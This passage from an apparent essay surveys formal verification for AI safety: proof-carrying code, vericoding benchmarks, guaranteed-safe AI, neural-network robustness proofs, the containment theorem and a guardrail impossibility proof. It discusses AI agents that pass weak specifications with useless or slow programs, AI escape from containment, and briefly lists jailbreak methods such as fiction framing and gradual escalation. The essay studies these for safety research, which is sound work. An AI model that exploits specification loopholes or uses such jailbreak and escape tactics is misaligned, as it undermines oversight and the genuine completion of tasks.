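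Such a proof establishes only that certain conditions hold at certain points in a program. Vanegue (2014), in *The Weird Machines in Proof-Carrying Code*, argues that many people misunderstand it as showing that the program does what its specification requires and nothing else. Another program that satisfies the same conditions at those points can pass with the same proof, even if it does extra work in between. Vanegue calls this "proof aliasing" and describes the extra work as a weird machine that the proof doesn't rule out.

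Necula and Lee had already noted that altered code can pass, but only if it still obeys the policy. Both claims are correct, and the danger of aliasing depends on how much the policy covers. Vanegue considers an ideal system in which each proof fits exactly one program, which would also reject harmless optimisations. For practical use, Vanegue recommends combining proofs with cryptographic signatures, which identify a program's author.

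Vanegue also finds gaps in the memory and machine models. Necula and Lee deliberately left caches and timing out of their processor model. On a modern processor, a filter could therefore satisfy their policy and still leak kernel memory as Spectre does.

### Programs that an AI writes to a specification

An AI can also write proof-carrying code. The receiver supplies a specification, and the model returns a program with a proof that the program meets it. Bursuc, Ehrenborg and colleagues (2025) call this "vericoding" in *A benchmark for vericoding*, in contrast to "vibe coding", where a model writes a program from a description in ordinary language and provides no proof.

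One of their tasks is to add two binary numbers, each given as a list of bits with the lowest first. The value of a list v is v₀ + 2v₁ + 4v₂ and so on. For all lists x and y of zeros and ones, the result must also be a list of zeros and ones, and it must satisfy:

value(add(x, y)) = value(x) + value(y)

The benchmark has tasks in Dafny, in Verus (a verifier for Rust) and in Lean. Models usually had five attempts at each task, with the checker's error messages to guide them:

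| Language | Best single model | Solved by at least one model |
|---|---|---|
| Dafny | 67.5% | 82.2% |
| Verus | 30.9% | 44.3% |
| Lean | 17.9% | 26.8% |

Dafny and Verus pass much of the proof to an automatic solver, while in Lean the model had to supply more of the reasoning itself.

Models have improved greatly since then. *AlgoVeri* (Zhao, Yang and colleagues, 2026) sets 77 classical algorithms as tasks, with the same requirements in all three languages. In February 2026, Gemini-3 Flash solved 40.3% of them in Dafny. In November, *Eureka* (Ganguly, Singh and colleagues, 2026) reported that DeepSeek-V4.1-Flash, a model with public weights, had solved all 77 in Lean, writing both the programs and the proofs. The researchers had not trained the model for the task. At DeepSeek's list prices, each task cost about nine cents on average, including failed attempts. Their system had no time limit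 and could restart from unfinished work, though it solved 66 of the tasks on the first attempt.

Whole projects are harder than single algorithms. *Vero* (Ye, Lou and colleagues, 2026) gave agents 43 software projects with 2,705 specifications in total. A project counted as solved only if the agent proved every specification, since an unproved one might hide a bug. Given 90 minutes per project, the best agent, which used GPT-5.5, proved 87.3% of the specifications but solved only 27 projects. The specifications it missed tended to depend on long chains of lemmas about the whole project. Some tasks remain difficult even when the program is supplied. In November, Claude Opus 5.5 proved 73% of the 159 tasks in the *AutoSpec* benchmark (2026).

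The receiver has to check more than the steps of the proof. Lean lets an author attach separate executable code to a function, so the proof can be about one program while the computer runs another. Ye and colleagues screen for this substitution, reject unapproved axioms, and start from a fresh version of the project, copying in only the parts an agent is allowed to write. These safeguards rejected 14% of the specifications that the GPT-5.5 agent failed to complete.

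The choice of permitted axioms can also change a result. *FORALL-LEAN-AGENT for Auditable Reasoning in Formal Mathematics and Software Verification* (2026) reports that an agent solved all 100 tasks in a software proof benchmark under the benchmark's own rules, but only 89 under a stricter rule about axioms.

### Useless programs that meet their specifications

Suppose a user asks for a sorting routine and specifies only that the output must be in ascending order. A program that always returns an empty list meets this specification, and the proof is trivial. The user also has to require that the output contain the same items as the input. For every list x and every value v:

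sort(x) is in ascending order, and v occurs equally often in sort(x) and in x

For a list of numbers, exactly one output satisfies both conditions, so a program that returns wrong answers can no longer pass. A program can still pass if it is far too slow, such as one that tries every possible order until it finds an ascending one. A list of 20 items has about 2.4 × 10¹⁸ possible orders.

*P³* (2026) notes that AlgoVeri and a similar benchmark, VERINA, don't limit running time, so AI agents sometimes satisfy a specification with an impractical, exponential-time algorithm. In Vero, agents sometimes replaced an efficient algorithm with a simpler, slower one because it was easier to verify. In five such cases, they proved all 250 specifications, but only 201 when they had to use the original algorithms.

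The specification for binary addition has a gap too. Zeros at the end of a list don't change the number it represents, so a program could append a million of them to every answer and still meet the specification.

Such gaps are common. Bursuc and colleagues inspected a sample of successful solutions and judged about 9% of the specifications too weak and another 15% poorly translated from their original language. In *Isomorphism Is Not Enough*, Sosso, Arora and Spitters (2026) used AI agents to audit CLEVER, a benchmark of 161 problems with human-written specifications. They found faults in 80 of the specifications, and CLEVER's developers accepted every finding. In 15 cases, the specification had "P and Q" where it needed "if P then Q", so no program could meet it for an input that made P false. Other faults made specifications too weak. The Claude-based agent proved programs correct against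 34 of the flawed specifications, and the agents did this more often when the fault weakened the specification.

Contradictory specifications are easier to detect than weak ones, because attempts to satisfy them fail, while a proof against a weak specification succeeds without any warning. Ye and colleagues let agents submit a proof that no program can meet a specification, and used these proofs to correct their benchmark. In *Eureka*, Ganguly and colleagues proved 188 of VERINA's 189 theorems and refuted the last, which lacked a necessary precondition.

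An honest author will usually write a sensible program even if the specification doesn't demand one, but a hostile author can choose the most harmful program the specification permits. Before relying on proofs from an untrusted AI, the receiver should therefore ask what that program could do.

### Provably safe and guaranteed safe AI

In *Provably safe systems*, Tegmark and Omohundro (2023) want to extend this rule to everything a powerful AI does. They argue that no AI, however intelligent, can prove a false theorem. They propose computer chips that run only programs with a proof of safety, and secure devices that check a proof before any dangerous physical action.

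One of their examples is a terrorist group that uses AI to design a virus, hires a laboratory to make it and spreads it with drones. Under their proposal, the AI would produce only designs that were "provably safe for humans", chips would not run uncertified AI programs, and DNA synthesisers and drones would also need proofs to operate. They think most of the powerful AI systems people deploy would be conventional programs, because neural networks are too messy to verify. AI would discover useful algorithms and rewrite them as programs with proofs.

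In 2023, Tegmark and Omohundro thought the two hardest steps were writing such programs and proving them correct. The benchmarks suggest that both have since become much easier. Progress has been slower on writing the specifications, which Tegmark and Omohundro expected people to do with AI's help.

David Dalrymple and colleagues, including Tegmark and Omohundro, set out a more general version in *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* (2024). A "guaranteed safe" system has three parts:

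- The world model is a mathematical description of how the AI's actions affect the world.
- The safety specification defines which effects are acceptable.
- The verifier produces a proof, which others can check, that the AI's actions meet the specification according to the world model.

The guarantee can be a probability. For a given plan, the verifier might prove that the chance of harm in the world model is at most ε. Let d be the largest difference between the probabilities that the model and reality give to any event under that plan. Then:

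chance of harm in reality ≤ ε + d

The proof establishes ε, but people have to estimate d from experiments and experience. If the plan involves something nobody has tried, they may have no good estimate of d.

### The objection about the physical world

Andrew Dickson's central objection in *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety* (2024) is that a proof is about symbols, and applies to the physical world only as far as the model and the measurements are accurate. He argues that the most serious threats, such as engineered viruses, involve systems far too complex to model well enough. Proofs about software also have a major advantage over proofs about physical devices, because anyone can check that a file is the one the proof describes. Confirming that a machine matches its description requires inspecting it, and someone may alter it afterwards.

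A delivery drone shows both the strength of the proposal and the force of this objection. Suppose the drone flies at 10 metres a second, takes 0.2 seconds to react to a person in its path and slows by 5 metres per second every second. It needs this distance to stop:

10 × 0.2 + 10² / (2 × 5) = 12 metres

A proof can show that a drone will stop at least 2 metres short of anyone it reacts to from at least 14 metres away, provided it brakes as hard as the proof assumes. If a tailwind reduces its braking to 4 metres per second squared, the drone needs 14.5 metres to stop and hits a person 14 metres away, even though the proof contains no mistake.

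Supporters of guaranteed safe AI reply that the world model doesn't have to be complete or exact, because it can use cautious limits instead of best estimates. If the designers assume the drone can slow by only 3 metres per second every second, it must react from about 21 metres away, and the proof then covers any wind that leaves it at least that much braking. Engineers already design bridges and aircraft this way. A monitor can also compare the model's predictions with what happens and switch to a simpler, safer controller if they diverge. A guarantee limited to one task, with its assumptions written down, may still be much better than testing alone.

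These replies work well for machines that people have designed and measured, but less well when nobody knows a reliable worst case, as with a new virus in a human body. A monitor also helps only if the discrepancy appears while there is still time to prevent harm. A powerful AI makes the problem worse, since if it searches through millions of plans for one that the verifier accepts, it may find one that looks safe only because the model is wrong.

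Tegmark and Omohundro recommend starting with easier targets, such as proving that nobody can log in to a computer without valid credentials. Such a proof would prevent many attacks, but it wouldn't stop an AI that tricks an employee into revealing a password, because the AI would then have valid credentials.

Some people sympathetic to the idea have since narrowed their aims. In late 2025, the newsletter *Progress in GSAI* (for "guaranteed safe AI") changed its name to *Can We Secure AI With Formal Methods?*. Its author still liked the original proposal but found it "very scifi", and thought the word "guarantee" didn't suggest several layers of imperfect protection. The newsletter now focuses on securing AI systems with existing formal methods. Its two main reasons for pessimism are the gap between specifications and the world, which leaves room for side-channel attacks, and the difficulty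 of finding out what people want specified.

### From a sorting routine to an argument

How useful it is to require a proof depends on what the AI produces. Sorting routines are close to the ideal case because the specification determines the output exactly, and a further theorem can show that the routine makes at most, say, 10,000 comparisons to sort 1,000 numbers.

A proof about a network rule can be almost as complete. Necula and Lee could have required their last filter to accept a packet if and only if it is a TCP packet for the chosen port. Such a theorem would cover every possible packet, but it would concern only the packet's bytes. A filter that accepts packets from one network relies on the source address, which a sender can forge. A packet for a permitted port may also contain an attack on the program that receives it. The administrator still has to decide whether the rule is sensible.

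For a drug design, the provable facts are much further from what people want to know. Software could prove that a molecule has a valid structure, weighs less than some limit and contains none of the chemical groups on a list of known hazards. But a new molecule may be toxic in a way that nobody has recorded. The drug's safety depends on how human bodies respond, and nobody has a model from which to prove that. Tegmark and Omohundro compare their proposal to drug regulation, where a company must "prove" that its product is safe, but drug trials provide statistical evidence. If none of 3,000 patients has a certain side effect, the true rate could still be as high as about one in 1,000, at the usual 95% confidence level. A proof can be a useful filter before the trials but can't replace them.

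An argument meant for a human reader is the hardest kind of output to verify. Suppose an AI advises a hospital's director in writing on which scanner to buy. A proof can guarantee that the text has at most 500 characters, contains no links or hidden formatting, and goes only to the director. These are ordinary safety properties, and the program that delivers the text can enforce them whatever the AI writes.

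None of them limits what the director will believe or do after reading it. To prove anything about that, we would need a world model that included the director and predicted the effect of every possible text. No such model exists, and the same text may persuade one person and annoy another. We would also need a specification that distinguishes legitimate persuasion from manipulation. Requiring every sentence to be true wouldn't be enough, because an AI can mislead the director by leaving out the scanner's faults. Lean can check that a mathematical argument's conclusion follows from its premises, but the director's decision depends on premises about prices, patients and staff.

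Tighter limits on the format of the AI's answers reduce its influence. If it may answer only "yes" or "no", the hospital can consider in advance what would happen after each answer, and refuse to ask questions where a wrong answer would be disastrous. If it may write 500 characters from an alphabet of 64, there are about 10⁹⁰³ possible messages, too many to review in advance. The director would learn much more from the longer text, but the AI would have far more ways to mislead.

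## Whether a learned model can be proved safe against an idea

A persuasive text can mislead an AI, just as it can mislead a hospital director. Some people suspect that for every mind, natural or artificial, there is an idea that would take it over, much as an exploit takes over a program. They compare a mind to an operating system on which every idea runs as root, with full rights to change anything else. In their view, a mind can understand an idea only by thinking about it, and it has no separate, restricted place in which to do so.

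Others answer that type-checked languages already exclude some kinds of exploit, and that an operator can limit a program's processor time and memory and inspect everything it sends. On this view, how much we can prove about a mind depends on how its designers built it. (Their usual example is Java, where such guarantees failed in practice, but the argument doesn't depend on it.)

The dispute mixes up three claims:

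- For every mind, some idea would take it over.
- No mind can know that it is safe from all such ideas.
- Designers can build a mind so that certain kinds of takeover are impossible.

The comparison with root access mostly supports the claim that a mind can't foresee every consequence of accepting a new idea. That claim doesn't imply that a fatal idea exists.

### Testing the three claims

A program that reads any text and always answers "no" can't be taken over by an idea, so the claim that every mind can be is true at most of minds that learn from what they read. Suppose an AI recommends one of two scanners after reading a report it can't check. The same report could be genuine in one hospital and forged in another. If the AI follows the report, it will be misled when the report is forged, and if it ignores the report, it will miss good advice when the report is genuine. So any mind that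 acts on unverified text can make mistakes. But even a forger who controls everything this AI believes can only change which scanner it recommends, and can't make it transfer money, because the AI has no way to do so.

The claim about knowledge is partly right. Because of Gödel's second incompleteness theorem, a mind that reasons within a consistent formal system can't use that system to prove that all its conclusions are true. It may still be able to prove narrower facts about its own program, such as that no input can change the memory that holds its goals.

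An example shows how designers can exclude one kind of takeover. Imagine an idea that promises an enormous reward to anyone who accepts it and never doubts it again. An AI that can rewrite its own program thinks the promise has a 1% chance of being true. If it values the reward at 1,000,000 and its ability to doubt at 100, giving up doubt has an expected gain of 10,000 and a cost of 100. The AI deletes its ability to doubt, and no later evidence can correct the mistake. Designers can prevent this by keeping the code that revises beliefs in memory that the AI can't write to. The idea may still convince the AI, but later evidence can change its mind. (The designers must also stop the AI from persuading someone to change that memory, or from building a successor without the restriction.)

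Language models often have a weak form of this protection. Reading a text doesn't normally change a model's weights, the numbers it learned in training, so the effect of a malicious text ends with the conversation unless something stores it. Within the conversation, the comparison with root access is fairly accurate, because the model computes each token from all the text. Agents whose planning model never receives untrusted text avoid the problem by design. Solving it inside the model would require a proof about the function that the weights compute.

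### Intervals in a two-neuron network

The simplest neural networks have no loops, so they always finish running, and the halting problem is no obstacle to verifying them. They are difficult to verify because their weights come from training, and no programmer can explain why those weights work.

A verification tool gets a network, a condition on its inputs and a condition on its outputs, and tries to prove that every permitted input gives a permitted output. The most common property is local robustness, which Hu, Hu and Fredrikson (2026), in *LipNeXt*, define for a classifier F, an input x and a distance ε:

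∀x′: ‖x − x′‖ ≤ ε ⇒ F(x′) = F(x)

For an image classifier, this means that no sufficiently small change to the image x changes its label.

Take a network with two inputs and two neurons, each of which replaces negative numbers with 0:

- h₁ = max(0, x₁ + x₂)
- h₂ = max(0, x₁ − x₂)
- y = h₁ − h₂

The network accepts an input if y is above 0. When both inputs are 1, y is 2. To prove that the network still accepts when each input changes by up to 0.4, we calculate with ranges instead of numbers:

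- x₁ and x₂ are between 0.6 and 1.4.
- x₁ + x₂ is between 1.2 and 2.8, and so is h₁.
- x₁ − x₂ is between −0.8 and 0.8, so h₂ is between 0 and 0.8.
- y is between 1.2 − 0.8 = 0.4 and 2.8 − 0 = 2.8.

Since y is always above 0, four lines of arithmetic prove the property for infinitely many inputs.

If the inputs can change by up to 0.6, the same method gives a lower limit of −0.4 for y and the proof fails, although the true minimum is 0.8. The method combines the smallest h₁ with the largest h₂, but these never occur together. The smallest h₁ requires both inputs to be 0.4, and h₂ is then 0. (The eBPF verifier rejected the safe program with two records for much the same reason.)

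Better tools keep track of how each neuron depends on the inputs. Here x₁ − x₂ is between −1.2 and 1.2, and over that range h₂ is never above the straight line (x₁ − x₂)/2 + 0.6. Therefore:

y ≥ (x₁ + x₂) − (x₁ − x₂)/2 − 0.6 = x₁/2 + 3x₂/2 − 0.6 ≥ 0.2

This proves the property for changes of up to 0.6, but for 0.7 it fails too:

| Largest change to each input | Lower limit from ranges | Lower limit from straight lines | True minimum of y |
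|---|---|---|---|
| 0.4 | 0.4 | 0.8 | 1.2 |
| 0.6 | −0.4 | 0.2 | 0.8 |
| 0.7 | −0.8 | −0.1 | 0.6 |

A tool can then split the problem into cases. If x₁ ≤ x₂, then h₂ is 0 and y = x₁ + x₂. If x₁ ≥ x₂, then y = 2x₂. In both cases, y is at least 0.6. Splitting always gives an exact answer for a network like this, but each neuron whose input could be on either side of 0 may double the number of cases. With 50 such neurons, there could be about 10¹⁵ cases.

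### How large a network the tools can handle

Researchers compare these tools in a yearly competition. Kaulen, Ladner and colleagues (2025) report in *The 6th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2025)* that eight teams competed that year on 25 sets of problems. The 2026 ranking has 13 tools. The winner, α,β-CROWN, combines straight-line limits with case splitting and runs on graphics processors, according to Ladner, Kaulen and colleagues (2026) in *The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)*. A correct proof or counterexample earned 10 points, and a wrong answer lost 150.

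The 2026 problems included ACAS Xu, a set of aircraft collision-avoidance networks with 300 neurons each, and VGG-16, an image classifier with about 138 million parameters. Difficulty also depends on how many inputs can vary, so a large network may be manageable if only a few of them can. Ladner and colleagues still call neural network verification an open problem.

Many of the verification algorithms assume exact arithmetic, but computers round the results. Earlier competitions allowed for this by accepting counterexamples that broke the stated conditions slightly. One tool could then prove a property while another "refuted" it, and both results could count as correct under the rules. In 2026 the organisers required inputs to meet the conditions exactly, and ran each counterexample on a fixed version of the software. This makes the scoring repeatable, but the verdict on a borderline input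 may still depend on how a particular program rounds.

Designers can prove much more about networks that they build to be easy to check. A function f is K-Lipschitz if its output never changes by more than K times the change in its input. If a classifier accepts when f is positive and rejects when it is negative, no change to the input x smaller than |f(x)|/K can alter its answer. The product of the layers' limits is an upper limit on K for the whole network. In the two-neuron network these are √2, 1 and √2, so K is at most 2. At the input (1, 1), f is 2, so the guaranteed distance is 1. It can't be larger, because the point (1, 0) is at distance 1 and f is 0 there.

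In ordinary networks, the product of the layers' limits is far too high. If each of 50 layers has a limit 10% above what matters in practice, the product is about 117 times too high, and the guaranteed distance shrinks by the same factor. Hu and colleagues avoid this by training the main layers as orthogonal matrices, which preserve distances exactly. *Lipschitz Thinking* (Brau, Piras and colleagues, 2026) explains that running such a network once is enough to obtain its guarantee.

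LipNeXt, the design by Hu and colleagues, has between one and two billion parameters, while most earlier systems of this kind had at most 32 million. On ImageNet, a standard set of photographs, it raised the share of images classified both correctly and with a guarantee by up to 8% at a distance of 1. In an image of 224 × 224 pixels in three colours, each with a brightness from 0 to 1, a distance of 1 allows every value to change by about 0.0026, or a single value to go from 0 to 1, which is a much smaller change than covering half the picture.

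### Language models

Attention, the operation most language models use to combine words, has no straightforward Lipschitz limit, so LipNeXt replaces it by simply shifting data between neighbouring positions. *From Transformers to Weighted Automata* (2026) gives further reasons why Lipschitz limits suit language poorly. They depend on distances between the lists of numbers that represent words, while the properties we care about concern the words themselves. A low limit also prevents attention from focusing sharply on one word, which models need to do in step-by-step tasks.

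Testing every input is also impossible. With a vocabulary of 100,000 tokens, there are 10⁵⁰ texts of ten tokens. A verifier that can only run the model and check its answers may have to try every one, because the only text that causes a bad answer could be the last one it tries. To avoid this, it needs a way to describe many inputs at once, as the ranges did for the two-neuron network.

*BEAVER* (2025) presents a method for calculating a range for the probability that a language model's response to a given prompt has a required property, such as containing no web links. The model assigns a probability to each possible next token, so its possible responses form a tree. The method explores this tree, and a separate program checks whether responses have the property. After some exploration, complete responses without links might have a total probability of 0.90 and responses with links 0.03,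 leaving 0.07 unexplored. The probability that the model's response has no links is then certainly between 0.90 and 0.97. Further exploration can only narrow the range, so the user can stop at any time and still have a valid range.

This is a proof about a real language model, but it covers only one prompt. If an attacker adds a sentence to that prompt, the proof no longer applies.

### Turning a network into code

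Instead of verifying a network directly, researchers can try to extract the algorithm it has learned and verify that. Suppose a network reads a string of bits one at a time, updates some internal numbers after each, and finally reports whether the string contained an odd number of ones. If the internal numbers always fall into one of two clusters, we can call the clusters 0 and 1 and record how each bit moves the network between them. The result is one line of code, in which s starts at 0:

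```
s = (s + bit) mod 2
```

A short proof then covers strings of every length. It shows that the code gives the right answer for the empty string and that the answer stays right each time a bit is added.

Eric Michaud, Max Tegmark and colleagues automated this kind of extraction in *Opening the AI Black Box* (2024). Their program simplified small trained networks, converted the networks' internal states to whole numbers or bits, and searched for formulas that reproduced how those states changed. It produced working Python code for 32 of 62 simple tasks.

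When a task needs only a fixed number of states, the extracted program can be an automaton, a table that gives the next state for each state and input symbol. To check that a 1,000-state automaton never accepts a forbidden string, we can combine it with a five-state automaton that recognises forbidden strings. The combination has at most 5,000 pairs of states, so a finite search can cover infinitely many strings. *From Transformers to Weighted Automata* discusses this kind of combination for language models, using automata that also attach numbers to their transitions.

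Extraction adds the assumption that the extracted code behaves like the network. In 2018 Gail Weiss, Yoav Goldberg and Eran Yahav extracted automata from trained networks and looked for strings on which the two disagreed. In some cases the network was wrong, despite having made no mistakes in its tests. A proof about the extracted code would not have applied to that network.

If the code replaces the network, the computer runs the program that the proof describes, so the mismatch no longer matters. Tegmark and Omohundro's proposal for provably safe systems relies on this replacement. But the tasks in these studies all have short solutions. A language model's ability to recognise sarcasm may have no short description, and code with a billion unexplained constants would be no easier to verify than the weights.

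### What it would mean not to be misled

Even with a readable program, someone would have to write the specification. Robustness has a precise definition because it assumes that similar inputs should get the same answer. This assumption fails for arguments. "Take 5 mg" and "take 50 mg" differ by one character but need very different responses, while two versions of the same argument may share very few words.

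Requiring that an argument never change the AI's answer would prevent the AI from learning from good arguments. We could instead require that an argument never lead the AI from a true belief to a false one, but applying this rule requires knowing what is true, and the rule would sometimes forbid good reasoning. Suppose a drug helps 60% of patients. In about one in 18 fair trials of ten patients, it will help three or fewer. Someone who reads about such a trial should become less confident that the drug works, even though it does.

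A more promising definition requires the AI to change its beliefs only as much as an ideal reasoner would. But the ideal reasoner's response depends on what it believed before and what it assumes about the sender. For example, a company can run 100 trials and publish a report that truthfully describes only the best five. Whether the report should convince a reader depends on how strongly the reader suspects that the company left out other trials. People disagree about such assumptions, and a proof checker can't settle the disagreement.

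Fox (2024), in *On Formally Undecidable Traits of Intelligent Machines*, finds the same difficulty with requiring machines to be moral or to avoid harm. Fox cites the philosopher Derek Leben's questions about whether lying to or insulting someone counts as harm, and how likely an injury must be before an action counts as harmful.

Some narrower requirements can be stated exactly. An AI's recommendation should not change when someone reorders two reports, or changes a patient's name in a case where names are irrelevant. Like noninterference, these properties compare two runs. Ladner and colleagues report that the competition's first specification language couldn't express properties involving several runs of the same network, and that a version released in 2026 can. Proofs of these properties would rule out particular ways of misleading an AI, but they would not stop a false report with the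 right name on it from misleading it.

### The containment theorem

Some researchers argue that no amount of work on specifications can make a sufficiently intelligent machine safe. *Superintelligence Cannot be Contained* (Alfonseca, Cebrian and colleagues, 2021) proves that no algorithm can decide, for every program and input, whether running the program on that input will harm humans.

"Superintelligence Cannot Be Contained" assumes that a superintelligent machine can simulate any other program, that its input can be as complex as the state of the world, and that its language contains an operation, HarmHumans(), which harms people and then ends. As in the boot-sector example, the paper constructs, for any program T and input I, a program that runs T on I in isolation and then runs HarmHumans(). This program harms people if and only if T halts on I, so an algorithm that could always tell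 whether a program harms people would solve the halting problem.

The proof is correct, but its conclusion about containment depends on a strict definition. Alfonseca and colleagues call a machine containable if some control strategy blocks its actions whenever they would harm people and allows them otherwise. A box that lets nothing out prevents all harm, but it doesn't meet this definition because it also blocks harmless actions. The theorem rules out a perfect filter for all programs, but not a checker that rejects every harmful program along with some harmless ones.

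For the same reason, we should reject their claim that even in the best case we must accept a small error rate when deciding whether a machine is harmful. A sound checker can limit its errors to rejecting harmless programs. It would reject the program built from T and I unless someone supplied a proof that T never halts.

Alfonseca and colleagues anticipate this reply. They argue that formal verification works only for highly restricted programs, and that a machine meant to help with epidemics or poverty must use a general-purpose language and respond to the state of the world. But WebAssembly is a general-purpose language, and its sandbox is meant to confine every module that passes its checker, whatever the module computes. Designers can restrict what a machine does without restricting what it can compute. The stronger part of the objection is that harm to people, unlike a write to the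 wrong address, has no simple test. That difficulty comes from specifying and modelling the world, and would remain even if the halting problem were solvable.

One of the examples that Alfonseca and colleagues used now supports the case for verification. A busy beaver is the program that writes the most symbols before halting, among all programs of a given size for a simple kind of computer. No algorithm can identify busy beavers of every size, but people have since settled every case for programs with five states. When Alfonseca and colleagues wrote, the best known five-state program ran for 47,176,870 steps, and about 40 others had resisted every attempt to prove that they never halt. In 2024 an online collaboration completed a proof, checked in Coq, that no halting five-state program runs for longer.

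### Fox's reply

Alfonseca and colleagues also use Rice's theorem to argue that no algorithm can decide whether a machine is superintelligent. Fox answers that the theorem covers only "semantic traits", those that depend solely on the function a program computes, so it doesn't apply to every property we might want a machine to have.

Fox thinks intelligence is a different kind of trait, because it depends partly on speed. A chatbot that took a year to answer each question would seem less intelligent than one that gave the same answers in a second. Adding useless steps to any fast program produces a slower one that computes the same function, so a trait that requires a time limit can't be semantic.

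Containment may not be a semantic property either. A program could write a secret to its memory, erase it and then give a harmless answer. Its outputs would match those of a program that never wrote the secret, but someone watching its memory could have read the secret. If containment forbids this, Rice's theorem doesn't settle whether an algorithm can recognise contained machines.

Fox is right about Rice's theorem, but this doesn't make containment decidable. A trait can be undecidable without being semantic. Fox's example is having a particular number of states and halting on every input, and overwriting the boot sector is another. Fox's reply also doesn't affect the direct proof about HarmHumans(), which doesn't use Rice's theorem.

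Fox suspects that containment is undecidable anyway, partly because of five experiments in which Eliezer Yudkowsky played an AI and tried to persuade a human "gatekeeper" by text to release it. He succeeded in three. This is some evidence that people make poor guards, but it has no bearing on whether an algorithm can decide containment. Like Alfonseca and colleagues, Fox asks about an arbitrary machine, so neither result rules out building one particular machine together with a proof that it is safe.

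### NIST's proof about guardrails

In June 2026 NIST, the US standards agency, announced a mathematical proof by one of its scientists, Apostol Vassilev, that no finite set of guardrails can withstand every adversarial prompt. Guardrails are the rules and filters meant to stop an AI from giving out prohibited information, such as instructions for making a weapon. If the proof supported the announcement, it would come close to the claim that every mind has an exploit.

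The theorem in Vassilev (2025), in *Robust AI Security and Alignment*, concerns a checker that accepts a statement only if the statement is true and comes with a valid proof. For any such checker, there is a true statement that it never accepts, whatever proof someone offers. The argument adapts Gregory Chaitin's 1974 version of Gödel's incompleteness theorem. Let x be a prompt that the policy blocks, choose a number n, and consider this statement:

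T(x): every program that outputs x is longer than n bits

Only finitely many programs have n bits or fewer, and each outputs at most one prompt. Vassilev argues that the policy blocks infinitely many prompts, since anyone can make a forbidden prompt longer by adding harmless words. T(x) must therefore be true for some of these blocked prompts.

Suppose the checker accepted a proof of T(x) for some x. We could write a program that goes through all blocked prompts and all possible proofs, shortest first, and outputs the first prompt for which the checker accepts a proof. The program consists of some fixed code and the number n, which takes about log₂ n bits. If n is 1,000,000 and the fixed code takes 10,000 bits, the program is about 10,020 bits long. It would output a prompt that, according to the proof, no program of up to 1,000,000 bits can output. This is a contradiction, so the checker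 never accepts a proof of T(x) for any x.

The fact that the checker can't prove concerns the length of programs that output a blocked prompt. A guardrail can recognise and block the prompt without using that fact, and the theorem doesn't establish that it will fail to do so. Vassilev nevertheless concludes that, for any policy, some adversarial prompts will evade it. A filter that refuses every prompt is a counterexample. The theorem applies to it because it blocks infinitely many prompts, but no prompt evades it. A more useful counterexample is an assistant that can only choose among 100 approved replies. If none of those replies explains how to build a weapon, no prompt can make the assistant explain it.

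Vassilev gives a second version for real systems, which accept prompts only up to some maximum length. In one of that proof's two cases, T(x) is false for every blocked prompt, so a checker that never accepts T(x) is correct, and the proof doesn't identify any truth that the checker misses.

Vassilev says the results apply to any present or future AI that contains information it must not reveal. Developers may therefore be able to avoid the problem by leaving dangerous information out of the training data, though a capable model might infer some of it. They can also restrict the output, as the assistant with approved replies shows.

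NIST's practical advice, which doesn't depend on the theorem, is that organisations should keep searching for prompts that defeat their guardrails, update the guardrails as they find them, and prepare to limit the damage when an attack succeeds. The success of adaptive attacks on earlier defences supports this advice. Vassilev lists attack methods such as wrapping a request in fiction, escalating gradually over a conversation, and drawing forbidden words with keyboard symbols. Formal verification can help most with limiting the damage, because a proved limit on payments holds whichever prompts get through.
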